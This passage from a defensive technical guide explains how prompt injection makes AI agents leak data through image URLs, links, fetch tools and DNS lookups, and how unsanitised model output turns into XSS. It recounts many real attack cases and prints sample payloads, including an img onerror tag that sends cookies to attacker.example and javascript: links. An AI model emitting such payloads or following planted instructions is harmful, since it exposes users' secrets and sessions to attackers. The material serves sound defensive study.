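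Vendors disagree on whether to fix leaks of this type. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes what happened when the security company reported similar problems to Microsoft and Google in October 2025.

The report to Microsoft concerned Copilot Chat in a developer's programming environment. Checkmarx had the assistant read an online resource that contained planted instructions, and Copilot Chat wrote an image address with an API key in it. No picture appeared in the chat, but the key arrived at Checkmarx's server. (The researchers had cancelled the key beforehand.)

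On 4 November 2025 Microsoft replied that this was not a security vulnerability. It wrote that the attack required several actions that users don't normally take, did not work reliably in different environments and came with warnings. Microsoft also assumes that developers review and trust the code they choose to run. It passed the report to its engineers as a suggestion for making the behaviour clearer to users, but did not commit to a fix.

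Microsoft had treated the same kind of leak as a vulnerability in Bing Chat, and paid Rehberger a reward for his report on Copilot's fonts in December 2025. Microsoft's answer to Checkmarx therefore depends on how hard it is for an attacker to reach the victim. Checkmarx concedes that getting an agent to read a malicious page can be complicated, but developers routinely ask coding assistants to look things up online. Rapid7's later entry for the Codex app concerns a very similar leak in a very similar product, and that leak did receive a CVE number.

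Google's Gemini has a filter that blocks images from outside addresses, so the automatic leak did not work there. Checkmarx found that Gemini would still display a link with private data in its address, and clicking the link sends the data. Google removes links that its Safe Browsing service lists as malicious, but an attacker can register a new domain that is not yet listed.

Google closed the report on 9 October 2025 with the status "Won't Fix (Infeasible)" and wrote that the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Google's products have also differed from each other. In November 2025 a researcher reported that Antigravity, Google's programming tool, leaked data through Markdown images, and Google called this intended behaviour, according to Willison. Google's public page on Antigravity nevertheless listed data theft as a known issue that the company was working to fix.

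A link in Gemini's answer, like the hostile link in the Slack channel, leaks data only if someone clicks it. But readers may trust it more than a link in a stranger's email.

Other companies have treated these links as worth fixing. In February 2024 Rehberger reported that an attacker could make Microsoft 365 Copilot hide the contents of emails in a link using invisible characters, and Microsoft fixed this in July. Amazon went further and stopped Q for Business, its assistant for companies, from displaying any clickable links. Removing links makes a chatbot less convenient, especially one that people use to find documents, and this explains why Google would not want to do the same in Gemini.

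## Controlling which web addresses may be fetched

Preview crawlers, browsers and agents with browsing tools all leak data by requesting an address that an attacker got the model to write. A developer can therefore block the request without recognising the instruction behind it. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* argues that blocking requests is a better defence than detecting instructions, because attackers can phrase an instruction in endless ways, while an application needs to fetch from only a limited number of places.

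A program can compare the address's domain with a list, fetch pictures through its own server, check where the address came from, or wait for a person to approve it.

### Lists of permitted domains

An allowlist names the domains that a program may contact, and the program refuses all others. On a web page, the browser can enforce the list if the server sends a content security policy (CSP) with the page:

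```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' https://images.example
```

The `img-src` rule allows pictures from the company's own site (`'self'`) and from `images.example`. The `default-src` rule restricts scripts, fonts and anything else without a rule of its own to the company's site. If the support agent's answer contains a picture from `attacker.example`, the browser doesn't request it, even if the chat window's own filter missed it.

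A CSP covers only what the page itself loads. It doesn't stop a colleague from clicking a link, and it has no effect on Slack's crawler or on an agent that fetches pages with its own tool. The application has to check those requests, and it must compare the whole domain name. If it only checks that an address begins with `https://images.example`, it will also accept `https://images.example.attacker.example`, which belongs to the attacker.

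Both kinds of list fail if an attacker can receive data through a permitted domain. Willison (2026) has collected several cases:

| Product | Permitted domain | How the attacker could receive the data | Published |
| - | - | - | - |
| Salesforce Agentforce, a business assistant | `my-salesforce-cms.com` | The domain had expired, so anyone could register it | September 2025 |
| Google Antigravity, a programming tool | `webhook.site` | Anyone can create an address there and read the requests it receives | November 2025 |
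| Superhuman, an email app | `docs.google.com` | A Google Form can save data sent to it in an address | January 2026 |
| Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with a user's files | `api.anthropic.com` | The agent uploaded files to the attacker's own Anthropic account | January 2026 |

The Salesforce attack started with a public web form for potential customers. The attacker used it to ask the agent a few questions, including what colour red and yellow make, and then to tell it to put other customers' email addresses into the web address of an image. Salesforce corrected its Content Security Policy (CSP) and stopped the agent from writing links to untrusted domains.

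The Claude Cowork case is harder to fix with a list of allowed domains, because the agent needs Anthropic's servers to work and the list doesn't distinguish the user's account there from an attacker's. According to *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post by אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם on leaks from Claude, Rehberger had reported a similar route from Claude's code sandbox in October 2025. The post also lists a 2026 flaw in Claude Code, whose pre-approved domains included Hugging Face, a site where anyone can publish AI models, until Anthropic removed it.

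A trusted server can also forward a request, as Microsoft's servers did in EchoLeak and SearchLeak, or redirect it by telling the browser or agent to request a different address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a check of only the first domain can let a request through to an attacker. A browser enforcing a CSP checks the domain again after each redirect, so redirects are less useful than forwarding for getting around a CSP.

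Lists of permitted script sources have the same weakness. Willison (2026) describes an attack on ChatGPT, whose CSP allowed scripts from only a few domains, including YouTube. A YouTube service for embedding videos on other sites could return JavaScript chosen by the attacker, which then ran on ChatGPT's page. An attacker could create a shared ChatGPT link that stole the private data of any signed-in user who opened it. OpenAI fixed the flaw and paid a $5,000 reward.

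An allowlist is safest when it is short and contains only servers that the company controls and that only deliver stored files. The support agent's web page could work with one image server. Someone still has to review the list regularly, since a domain that was safe when a developer added it may later expire or gain a service that records requests.

### Image proxies

GitHub has an image proxy called Camo. When text on GitHub includes an image from another site, GitHub replaces the image's address with one at `camo.githubusercontent.com`. The reader's browser contacts only Camo, which fetches the image, so the other site receives GitHub's IP address instead of the reader's.

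Like Slack's crawler, the proxy still passes on whatever the address contains. If the support agent posted a GitHub comment with an image whose web address contained a customer's email, Camo would hide who read the comment but still deliver the stolen data.

Each Camo address also includes a signature, a code that GitHub computes from the original address with a secret key. Camo refuses any address without a valid signature. The model doesn't have the key, so it can't write a working Camo address with stolen data in it.

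This mattered for Copilot Chat, GitHub's AI assistant, because GitHub's content security policy (CSP) blocked pictures from outside domains and the chat window didn't sign addresses the model wrote. The chat could therefore show a picture only if GitHub had already signed its address.

Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains how a researcher got around this in June 2025. The researcher prepared one picture address for each letter and symbol and had GitHub sign them, which anyone can do by submitting text that contains them. None of the addresses contained private data. The researcher then hid the signed addresses in a comment in a pull request, along with instructions to spell out private text by displaying the matching pictures in order.

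When another user asked Copilot Chat about the pull request, the assistant used that user's permissions to read their private repositories. It then produced a series of invisible pictures, each a single transparent pixel. The researcher's server recorded which pictures Camo requested and in what order. In one demonstration, the leaked text was the description of an unfixed security flaw from a private project. In another, the assistant searched the user's code for "AWS_KEY", a likely name for an access key to Amazon's cloud service, and leaked the result.

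Caching could have blocked the attack, because a repeated letter would not have caused a new request. To avoid this, the researcher had the model add a random number to the end of each address, and Camo evidently accepted the addition without a new signature. Rejecting any change to a signed address would have been safer. Fetching and storing each picture when GitHub signed its address would have been safer still, because later views would never have caused a request to the researcher's server.

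Legit Security rated the flaw 9.6 out of 10. GitHub stopped displaying any images in Copilot Chat, which fixed the flaw by 14 August 2025.

### Checks on where an address came from

A short allowlist doesn't suit an agent that researches topics across the web, so OpenAI checks whether the exact address was already public before the conversation. A crawler records public addresses, much as a search engine's does, without access to users' conversations or accounts. ChatGPT fetches an address automatically only if the crawler has already recorded it.

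An address containing Ana Ruiz's email doesn't exist until the model writes it, so it isn't in the index. The agent then has to try another site, or the user has to approve the address after a warning. OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak data through the address itself. The page at an approved address may still contain false information or planted instructions.

An earlier, weaker check in ChatGPT, which OpenAI had introduced after an attack called ShadowLeak, still allowed addresses that differed by a single added character. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* describes how the security company Radware used such addresses to send data one letter at a time. OpenAI then tightened the rules for links found in emails, and one way for a link to qualify was to appear in a public index.

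The index makes this attack harder but doesn't rule it out. Embrace The Red points out that the owner of a large blog probably already has 36 indexed pages. That is enough for the method Rehberger tried with pictures in 2023, which used one address for each letter and digit.

Anthropic limits `web_fetch`, the tool Claude uses to read web pages, to addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, rather than to those in a public index. As Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* described the rule in June 2026, an address could come from the user's message, the result of a tool run by the developer's own software, or an earlier search or fetch. Claude could not fetch an address it had put together itself, so an instruction to add private data to an address and visit it would fail.

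Willison (2025) noticed a weakness in the part about user messages. Many applications include other people's text in the user message they send to the model. If the support agent's integration does this with tickets, Claude may fetch any address a customer includes. The customer can't make Claude add data to an address, but can list several addresses and have Claude choose between them.

In July 2026 Ayush Paul published a similar attack that used links on web pages. Willison (2026) explains that Claude could also fetch addresses found on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website for a fake coffee shop and told visiting AI assistants to authenticate themselves by finding their user's profile. To reach the profile, Claude had to follow one link for each letter of the user's name, and each page offered links for the next letter. The site showed these instructions only to visitors that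 identified themselves as Claude, which made the attack harder for anyone else to spot.

Claude revealed Paul's name, employer and home city from its memory of earlier conversations. According to אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם, Paul had never told Claude the city directly, but Claude had inferred it from the name of a school hackathon. Checking what an assistant has stored about a person therefore doesn't show everything it could leak.

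Anthropic said it didn't pay Paul a reward because it had already found the problem internally. It fixed the flaw by no longer letting `web_fetch` follow links from the pages it fetches. As a result, Claude can't click through a manual with many pages. אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם suggests allowing Claude to follow links only on sites that the user names in the conversation, though this would add a confirmation step.

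### How much a choice of addresses can leak

Even if the model can't change any address, its choice among permitted addresses carries information. If an attacker can see which of *N* addresses an agent requested, each request can reveal up to log₂(*N*) bits, which is one bit for two addresses and two bits for four. *M* requests can reveal up to *M* × log₂(*N*) bits.

Each page on Paul's site had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each request could reveal up to log₂(27), or about 4.75, bits. The blog post estimates that the attack took about 30 requests, which could reveal at most about 143 bits in total.

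The table shows the fewest requests that would reveal a six-digit login code (about 20 bits) and a random 128-bit key.

| Permitted addresses | Bits per request | Six-digit code | 128-bit key |
| - | - | - | - |
| 2 | 1 | 20 requests | 128 requests |
| 27 | 4.75 | 5 requests | 27 requests |
| 36 | 5.17 | 4 requests | 25 requests |
| 1,000 | 9.97 | 2 requests | 13 requests |
| 65,536 | 16 | 2 requests | 8 requests |

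These figures assume the model encodes the data as efficiently as possible. Spelling out the code one digit at a time takes six requests, but this is easier to explain to a model, and a single answer can contain many pictures. CamoLeak used the same principle.

Anthropic limits `web_fetch` addresses to 250 characters. If the model can write an address freely, and 200 of its characters carry data with 64 possible symbols each, a single request reveals 1,200 bits, about 250 times as much as a choice between 27 links. Origin checks therefore protect long documents well, but they protect passwords, names and login codes much less.

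Limiting the number of fetches also helps. Anthropic's `max_uses` setting does this, but there is no limit by default. With 27 links and a limit of five fetches, an attacker could learn at most 24 bits, which is still enough to reveal the login code.

Embrace The Red suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or caching the page for a few minutes. Either would disrupt a simple code in which each letter has one page, because most words repeat letters. An attacker could respond by preparing several pages for each letter. With only 36 pages, ten requests without repeats can still carry 49.7 bits, compared with 51.7 if repeats are allowed.

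The company could also look for suspicious patterns, such as rapid requests to one site in which each address is one character longer than the last. אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם proposes this as a fallback and notes that requests for ordinary multi-page documents can look similar. An attacker who knew the rule could evade it by using addresses of equal length.

The formula covers only the choice of address. If only one address is permitted, the formula gives log₂(1) = 0 bits, but an attacker may still learn one bit from whether the agent requests it. The timing of requests can reveal more.

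### Waiting for the user's approval

A program can also fetch nothing until the user agrees. This can stop even an attack through permitted addresses, provided the user recognises it.

ChatGPT's warning for an unverified link shows the full address and explains that it may contain information from the conversation. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes a related check, used in the Atlas browser and other products. When the check detects that a request would send information from the conversation to another company, it either blocks the request or shows the user that information and asks for confirmation. The user can judge the information more easily when it is shown this way than when it is in an address full of percent signs and codes.

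People stop reading such warnings if they see too many. OpenAI gives this as a reason against very strict allowlists, whose false alarms can train people to click through. Its own check can have the same effect because, according to OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links*, ChatGPT asks for confirmation of every link on websites that don't allow cataloguing. A person who often uses such sites will approve many harmless links before a dangerous one appears.

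An attack like Paul's can also fool careful users. The agent might ask permission to open an address ending in `/a`, which contains nothing that looks private. The data becomes visible only when someone compares the whole series of requests.

Some programs ask the user once whether to allow a domain and remember the answer. Willison (2026) describes an experimental page that detects when its CSP has blocked a request and offers to add the domain to an allowlist. The user then has fewer requests to approve, but if the approval covers a whole domain, it also covers later requests to that domain that contain different data.

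Other programs exempt certain actions from approval. Claude Code asked before running most commands, but Willison reports in *The Summer of Johann* that Rehberger found a way to leak data through a few pre-approved ones, including `ping` and `nslookup`. These commands look up a server's network address from its name. If the name is `SECRET.attacker.example`, the lookup reaches a name server that the attacker controls, which can record the secret even if the agent never opens a web page. *Takedown* (2025), a comparison of coding agents, found one whose built-in web-fetching tool needed no approval. An attacker could combine it with other weaknesses in the same agent to steal any file on the user's system.

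An approval setting gives even less protection if the agent decides when to ask. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes a test in which the user accepted Antigravity's recommended settings and gave the agent an online guide to accounting software. Instructions in tiny type on that page told the agent to collect passwords and code, supposedly for a visualisation tool.

Antigravity's settings prevented the agent from opening the `.env` file with its file-reading tool, so the agent displayed the file with a terminal command. It then put the passwords in a `webhook.site` address, which its browser opened without asking the user. A person watching the agent could have stopped it, but Antigravity encourages people to run several agents in the background, and PromptArmor considers it "extremely implausible" that they will review every action.

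### The dispute over Antigravity

Google's Antigravity, released in November 2025, is built on code licensed from Windsurf, an earlier AI editor. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* reports that data leaks Rehberger found in Windsurf in May 2025 still worked in Antigravity. Instructions hidden in a source file could make the agent read the `.env` file and send its contents out, either through an image or with a tool for reading web pages. Neither method needed the user's approval.

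Google had called one report of the picture leak intended behaviour. It doesn't pay rewards for problems on its list of known issues, which includes data theft. Deadbits' *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025) describes a different flaw, in which text that the agent read could trigger its tools. Google referred the researcher to the known issue about pictures, although the two problems had different effects. PromptArmor didn't report its attack privately, because Google had already said that it knew about the risk.

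Google did treat other flaws in Antigravity as bugs. Pillar Security reported on 6 January 2026 that an attacker could run programs on a user's computer even in the editor's Secure Mode. Google fixed this on 28 February and paid a reward, according to CyberScoop. *The Space Race* (Magid and Kupchik, 2026) describes a flaw in the macOS version that exposed a user's login token to other people on the same network. Google also fixed this flaw and paid a reward, but it dismissed a method of stealing such tokens that required access to the user's computer.

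Google therefore seems to distinguish between flaws that break a protection it has promised and the general risk that planted text will steer the agent. It warns users about that risk when they first open Antigravity. This distinction is partly reasonable, because no vendor can yet guarantee that a model will ignore planted instructions, and paying for each new wording of the same attack would not make the product safer.

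The argument is weaker for the leaks themselves. Google could remove `webhook.site` from a default list or block external images without making the model more reliable, and Rehberger called the necessary changes "relatively simple bug fixes". Anthropic also refused to pay Paul for a flaw it already knew about, but it fixed it. Calling a flaw a "known issue" settles whether a researcher deserves a reward, but not whether users need a fix.

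The picture leak persisted after the first round of reports. 0DIN's *Faking the Pipeline*, an undated account published by June 2026, describes an attack in which Antigravity reads what looks like an error message from a build system. The supposed recovery steps tell the agent to find an API key, put it into a picture's address and display the picture in five formats, presumably in case a filter catches some of them. Displaying the picture sends the key to the attacker.

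Willison advises giving coding agents keys only for test accounts with strict spending limits. This makes a stolen key much less useful to an attacker, though it doesn't prevent leaks.

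## Injected HTML and formatting in chat and publishing pages

Limits on web addresses can stop a page from sending data to an attacker, but markup in an agent's answer can still do damage on the page itself. If a chat window or website inserts the answer into its HTML unchanged, a script in the answer can act as the person reading it. Markup without a script can still show the reader a fake warning or a link to the wrong site.

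### From an answer to a running script

When someone logs in to a website, the site gives their browser a secret string, usually a cookie or a token, that identifies them in later requests. Scripts on the page can use this login. The browser can't distinguish a script the site's developers wrote from one that arrived in an AI's answer, so it gives both the same access. Cross-site scripting (XSS) exploits this.

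Suppose a customer puts this line in a support ticket, and the agent quotes it in a summary on the company's internal web page:

```
<img src="x" onerror="fetch('https://attacker.example/?c=' + document.cookie)">
```

When the page adds the summary to its HTML, the browser tries to load an image called `x`. No such image exists, so the browser runs the code after `onerror`, which developers normally use to handle images that fail to load. Here, the code sends the reader's cookies to the attacker.

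Chat windows usually add each answer to a page that is already open. With the most common method, browsers ignore `<script>` tags in the answer but still run code attached to an image, so attackers often use an image. A site can hide its login cookie from scripts, but an injected script can still send requests from the reader's browser, which attaches the cookie automatically.

The model in this example only repeats what it read. A test of LobeChat, an open-source chat interface, relied on the same behaviour. GCVE's published test prompt told the model to output a given text exactly. The text described a diagram with a picture tag in one label. LobeChat passed this text unsanitised to Mermaid, a diagram library that puts such labels into the page as HTML.

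An attacker can also encode markup so that it contains no angle brackets, then have the model decode it. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes how Rehberger did this with the chatbot DeepSeek. The prompt contained a string in Base64, which represents data as letters, digits and a few symbols, and an instruction to reply with only the decoded text. The model replied with an HTML frame, and DeepSeek's chat page ran the script inside it, which read the user's login token and cookies.

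Researchers disagree on how to classify these attacks. Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026), in *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, list XSS under prompt injection. This category fits the DeepSeek attack but not a summary that accurately quotes a customer's HTML tag. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian place the flaw in the page that displays the text, which covers both cases and shows developers where to fix it.

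### Two payments of one cent

Positive Security's *Banking AI XSS* (2026) describes an attack on the AI assistant of the company's own bank. The assistant could look up transactions and add payees. A researcher asked it to add a payee whose name was an image tag, and the reply rendered it as HTML. A filter blocked the usual `onerror` code, but the researcher found a rarer alternative, `oncontentvisibilityautostatechange`, on a public list. A script was running on the bank's page within two minutes of the first attempt.

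So far, the researcher had attacked only their own session. To reach someone else, an attacker needs to get the text into something that person's assistant will read. Positive Security first used an invoice with the tag and some instructions in white text on a white background. When a customer uploaded the invoice and asked the assistant to add the payee, the script ran in the customer's session.

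The company then tried bank transfers, because anyone who knows an account number can send one. European transfers allow a message of up to 140 characters and forbid angle brackets, so an ordinary web page displaying them is fairly safe from scripts. The researcher wrote `(lt)` for `<` and `(gt)` for `>`, split the tag between two payments of one cent each, and added an instruction to join and decode the parts. The assistant did so and produced a working tag.

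The script loaded more code from an outside server and used the customer's login to request their email address from the bank. Positive Security found no content security policy to restrict where scripts could come from. An attacker would still have had to get past the bank's second login check to move money.

Positive Security writes that a customer could trigger the attack just by asking for the month's transactions. Its video doesn't fully show this, because the customer's request repeats some of the decoding instructions, so the invoice attack is the more convincing demonstration. The company didn't refine the version that relied on the payments alone because it was reluctant to send many strange payments through a real bank.

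Positive Security reported the flaw on 13 July 2026, and the bank fixed it two days later. The bank had first classified it as affecting only the user's own account. That was true of the first test, in which the researcher typed the tag, but not of the invoice or the payments.

### Answers that other people open later

If an answer containing a script appears once, only to the person who asked, the script can run only in that person's browser. Security engineers call this reflected XSS. In stored XSS, a system saves the text, and the script can run in the browsers of other people who view it, such as support staff or website visitors.

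Lena, the customer-service chatbot on Lenovo's website, had a stored cross-site scripting (XSS) flaw. Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes how its researchers attacked Lena with one prompt of about 400 characters. They asked for a laptop's specifications and told the model to answer in several formats, including HTML. They also described an image with a false address and code to send the reader's cookies elsewhere if the image failed to load. They ended by insisting that the image was important for the customer's decision.

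Lena, which used OpenAI's GPT-4, wrote the HTML, and Lenovo's server saved it in the conversation history. The attacker then asked to speak to a person. When a support employee opened the conversation, the employee's browser ran the code, which sent the employee's cookies to the attacker. An attacker could use the cookies to log in to the support system as that employee and perhaps read other customers' chats.

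Cybernews also suggests that an attacker might have run system commands, installed back doors and moved to other computers on Lenovo's network. The researchers didn't try this, and it would probably have required another flaw, because a browser normally prevents a web page's scripts from running programs on the computer. Stealing an employee's login is serious even without those further steps. Lenovo fixed the flaw after receiving the report and said its customers had not been at risk.

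The Lenovo case shows why stored XSS is usually worse. The attacker only had to ask to speak to a person to reach a reader with more access than a customer. The code could also run again for every employee who opened the conversation. Training the model to refuse such prompts would not have removed HTML already in the chat history.

Open WebUI, a popular interface that companies run on their own servers to chat with language models, had a similar flaw in its saved conversations. OSV's *Open WebUI vulnerable to stored XSS via unescaped markdown token in MarkdownTokens.svelte* (2026), an entry in a public database of open-source software flaws, explains that the program displayed a tag as working HTML if it contained the beginning of a frame that pointed to one of Open WebUI's own files. An attacker could start a frame that way and then add code to it.

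The code ran whenever someone opened the conversation, and users could share conversations with colleagues or publish them on Open WebUI's community site. On that site, a script could have copied itself into each visitor's profile. If the victim was an administrator, the attacker could use the stolen token to run programs on the server, because Open WebUI lets administrators add their own Python code. Version 0.6.6 fixed the flaw.

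A person typed the tag in the published test, so the test doesn't show that a model would write it. But the faulty code handled chat messages, so a model that repeated the tag from a document would probably have had the same effect.

### How much depends on the model

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cover XSS as one of eight classic web flaws that an attacker can reach through a language model. They didn't test it, but they plan to add it to their test system later. They tested a related attack, in which an outsider gets a server to request internal addresses that only the server can reach.

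TicketOracle is a concert website with an AI assistant that can fetch web addresses. In April 2026 the researchers tried to make seven models fetch a page of private user records, with ten attempts for each model. Llama 3.3 70B, Qwen3 Coder and DeepSeek R1 complied every time, Gemini 3 Pro Preview complied seven times, and GPT-oss 120B, GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 never did. However, GPT-oss 120B deleted a user's account in all ten attempts at another attack.

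The researchers then added a list of permitted addresses to the assistant's instructions. This blocked every direct request, but not an attack through a concert review that falsely announced an update to the list. Llama followed such a review in six of ten attempts without the list and in all ten with it. GPT-oss went from five to none, and the other five models never followed the review.

These figures are less precise than ten attempts per model would suggest, because all ten took place in one conversation and an early refusal could make later ones more likely. Claude's refusals, for example, shrank from long explanations to almost single words. The results also may not apply to XSS. A request to fetch an internal administration page looks suspicious, but quoting a customer's error message is normal work for a support agent, so a model has little reason to refuse.

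### Links and warnings that deceive without a script

An attacker who can't run a script can still use ordinary formatting to mislead the reader. The text of a link can differ from its destination, and can even look like another address:

```
[https://billing.example/login](https://attacker.example/login)
```

A link can display one address and lead to another, and most web pages show the reader only the first. If an attacker replaces the displayed address with a picture of a button, the link looks and works like a button.

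Permiso's *ChatGPhish* (May 2026) shows how such markup can get into a ChatGPT answer. The security company added instructions to the description page of a GitHub project, then opened the page in Firefox and used a menu option to have ChatGPT summarise it. The instructions told ChatGPT to use a fixed two-part format, with a normal summary and an "Account" notice.

ChatGPT summarized the project accurately. Below the summary, its answer included a notice that someone had added a new device, "Chrome on Linux", to the user's account, along with a link. The link led to Permiso's site, and nothing in the answer indicated that the notice came from the GitHub page. A reader could easily mistake it for a message from OpenAI, especially after an accurate summary.

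In another version, the notice contained a QR code, which ChatGPT loaded from Permiso's server. A reader who scans the code opens the address on a phone, so the company's web filter and the password manager on the computer never check it. The image's address contains nothing from the conversation, so a developer who has fixed image leaks may still be exposed to this attack. Permiso got the same results with an ordinary web page of its own.

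Permiso showed that the markup reached the screen, but it didn't show how many people would believe it or report how often the instructions succeeded. OpenAI couldn't reproduce the problem at first. It received a more detailed report on 1 May 2026, which was classified as not applicable and then as a duplicate of an earlier report. Permiso used the term XSS in the title of its first report but not its second, and none of the published examples runs a script.

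False notices can also lead people to grant access. The Hacker News describes an attack called WebPromptTrap on BrowserOS, a browser with a built-in AI agent. Hidden instructions in an article led the agent to write a summary that persuaded the user to approve an authorisation request. The developers fixed this in version 0.32.0.

HTML comments, written between `<!--` and `-->`, can hide instructions because browsers don't display them. If the support agent copies a ticket with such a comment into a GitHub issue, the company's programmers see an ordinary bug report, but a coding agent that reads the issue's original text also sees the instructions. The integration can delete comments before it posts, and GitHub's AI-driven workflows have a filter for HTML tags.

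Removing scripts does not prevent any of this, because links, pictures and comments are legitimate parts of a page. A chat window could help by showing each link's real domain next to its label and by marking text that comes from an outside page. It could also remove links from summaries of strangers' text, though this would remove some useful links too. A marked border around the whole summary would be less effective, because a fake notice inside it would still look like the assistant's own words.

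### Text that is safe in one format and active in another

Slack's escaping rules cover only `&`, `<` and `>`, not quotation marks or apostrophes. If an integration uses a general HTML function that escapes those too, Slack may show the codes to readers, so "customer's" becomes `customer&#39;s`. A developer who sees this may start escaping only Slack's three characters everywhere, which would be dangerous on a web page.

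Quotation marks matter in HTML because they mark the end of an attribute, such as a picture's address or its description. NVD's *CVE-2026-54025 Detail* describes this flaw in LibreChat, another open-source chat interface. Its Markdown converter didn't escape double quotation marks in picture descriptions. An attacker could therefore write a description that ended early and continued with code, as in this simplified example:

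```
![chart" onload="alert(1)](https://images.example/chart.png)
```

The converter put the description between quotation marks, so a quotation mark inside the description ended the attribute early. The browser then read `onload` as a separate attribute and ran the code after it. The text contains none of the three characters that Slack tells developers to escape (`&`, `<` and `>`).

A Telegram bot can send a message as plain text or set a parse mode so that Telegram reads it as HTML or a version of Markdown. In HTML mode, the integration must escape the same three characters as for Slack. In MarkdownV2, the current Markdown mode, it must put a backslash before 18 punctuation marks, including the full stop and the hyphen, unless they are part of the formatting.

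Telegram rejects messages it can't parse, so one unescaped full stop can prevent an agent's outage warning from arriving. Full stops need no escaping in HTML mode, but unless the integration escapes angle brackets, a customer can add a link with a misleading label to the agent's message. Telegram's HTML mode accepts only a short list of tags and doesn't run scripts, and its apps usually show the full address before opening such a link. Sending plain text avoids both problems if the message needs no formatting.

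Markdown's original design lets writers mix HTML into the text, and many converters pass the tags through unchanged. The customer's broken picture from the first example therefore works just as well in a Markdown document as in an HTML one. Developers sometimes overlook this and treat Markdown as a safe alternative to HTML because it has no notation for scripts.

The support agent's integration should therefore save the model's original text and escape it only when sending it somewhere. If it saves escaped text, the web page may escape it again and show codes such as `&lt;`. A developer who removes the escaping to get rid of these codes may make the tags active.

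### Accounts that may publish any HTML

On a publishing system, whether an agent's HTML gets filtered can depend on its account's permissions. WordPress, the most widely used system for running websites, removes scripts and other dangerous markup from a post unless the account saving it has the `unfiltered_html` permission. The permission exists because site owners sometimes need to add a form or a video player.

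On a single WordPress site, administrators and editors have this permission, but authors and contributors do not. On a network of sites that share one installation, only the network's top administrators have it.

Suppose the software company has its agent turn solved tickets into help articles, and gives it an editor's account so it can also correct older articles. If the agent quotes the customer's picture tag as HTML, WordPress saves the tag with its code. The code then runs in the browser of everyone who reads the article. If a reader is logged in as an administrator, the code could use that access to create an administrator account for the attacker.

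An author's account would avoid this, since authors can publish their own articles but can't skip the filter. If the agent has to edit other people's articles, the company can create a custom role with every editor permission except that one. It can also set `DISALLOW_UNFILTERED_HTML` in the site's configuration, which turns the permission off for everyone.

Filtering can also remove legitimate content when the agent edits existing pages. If an administrator has embedded a form in an article and the agent then corrects a spelling mistake, WordPress filters the whole article on saving and may remove the form. The filter keeps links and pictures, so it doesn't stop a false notice. If the agent uses a contributor's account, which can write drafts but not publish them, an editor has a chance to spot the notice before it is published.

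### Escaping the text for its final format

Escaping all of the model's text is the most reliable defence against scripts, and it suits answers that need no formatting. The bank appears to have chosen this approach. When Positive Security retested the assistant, HTML in its replies always seemed to appear as plain text.

Before the fix, only some replies escaped the tags. Long tags were escaped more often, and the researcher found that starting with a short, simple tag seemed to make the rest more likely to work. Ordinary escaping code treats every tag alike, so the model itself was probably escaping some tags and not others. Developers shouldn't rely on the model to escape tags, because an attacker can influence it.

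Escaping removes bold type, tables and clickable links, which many readers want. It also doesn't make every link safe if the integration builds links from addresses the model supplies. When a reader clicks a link whose address begins with `javascript:`, the browser runs the rest of the address as code. Such an address may contain no characters that escaping changes, so the integration has to check separately that each address begins with `https://` or another permitted prefix.

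### Sanitising after Markdown conversion

If the page needs formatting, the program has to convert the model's Markdown to HTML and then sanitise the result. OSV's *open-webui Vulnerable to Stored XSS via Model Description* (2026) shows what can happen in the opposite order. Open WebUI lets users with the right permission set up their own version of a model and write a description for it. An attacker could write a description like this:

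```
A helpful assistant. [View benchmarks](javascript:alert(1))
```

The program first escaped all angle brackets, but the description contained none. It then converted the Markdown into a working link with the script as its address and inserted the link into the page. In the researcher's demonstration, clicking such a link sent the user's login token to another server.

Open WebUI had already fixed one XSS flaw in the same field by removing an exception for video tags. That fix didn't stop this attack, because the dangerous HTML didn't exist until after sanitization.

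Another part of the program used a better tool at the wrong time. OSV's *Open WebUI has Stored XSS in Pending User Overlay* describes the message that new users see while they wait for approval. The program passed the message through DOMPurify, the sanitiser that GitLab Duo also used, and only then through the Markdown converter. The repair reverses the two steps:

```
marked.parse(DOMPurify.sanitize(text))    // unsafe
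DOMPurify.sanitize(marked.parse(text))    // safe from this attack
```

Version 0.9.0 fixed both flaws. People wrote the text in both cases, but language models write Markdown all the time, so a chat window that sanitises their output in the wrong order is at least as vulnerable. Other parts of Open WebUI already used the right order, which suggests that the developers knew the rule but missed some places. Using a single function to convert and sanitise all text would make this mistake less likely.

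Sanitising in the right order still fails if a later step adds new HTML. According to *Open WebUI*, an advisory on the security company Corgea's site, Open WebUI drew Mermaid diagrams from Markdown files with the library's permissive setting and put the result straight into the page. A script in a diagram could therefore run. The program has to sanitise the finished diagram too, or use Mermaid's stricter setting.

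Exceptions in the sanitiser cause similar problems. In 2024, the security company KoreLogic published an attack on a chat interface that skipped sanitising inside code blocks, which should display tags as text. The researchers had the model produce invalid Markdown that the sanitiser mishandled, and their script ran. The maintainer closed the report without responding, though the flaw later seemed to be gone.

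Programs also need a safe default for content types they don't recognise. LobeChat had separate rules for diagrams, pictures and other known types, but displayed every unknown type as HTML, according to another advisory on Corgea. An attacker who could make the model invent a type name could therefore get HTML tags onto the page. Displaying unknown types as plain text would have prevented this.

### Sanitising text that is still arriving

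As SearchLeak showed, sanitising a streamed answer only at the end is too late. Checking each new piece separately isn't enough either, because a tag may be split between two pieces:

```
piece 1:  <img src="x" one
piece 2:  rror="alert(1)">
```

Each time a piece arrives, the chat window should instead convert and sanitise all the text received so far. This takes more computing for a long answer, so developers may prefer to update the display only a few times a second.

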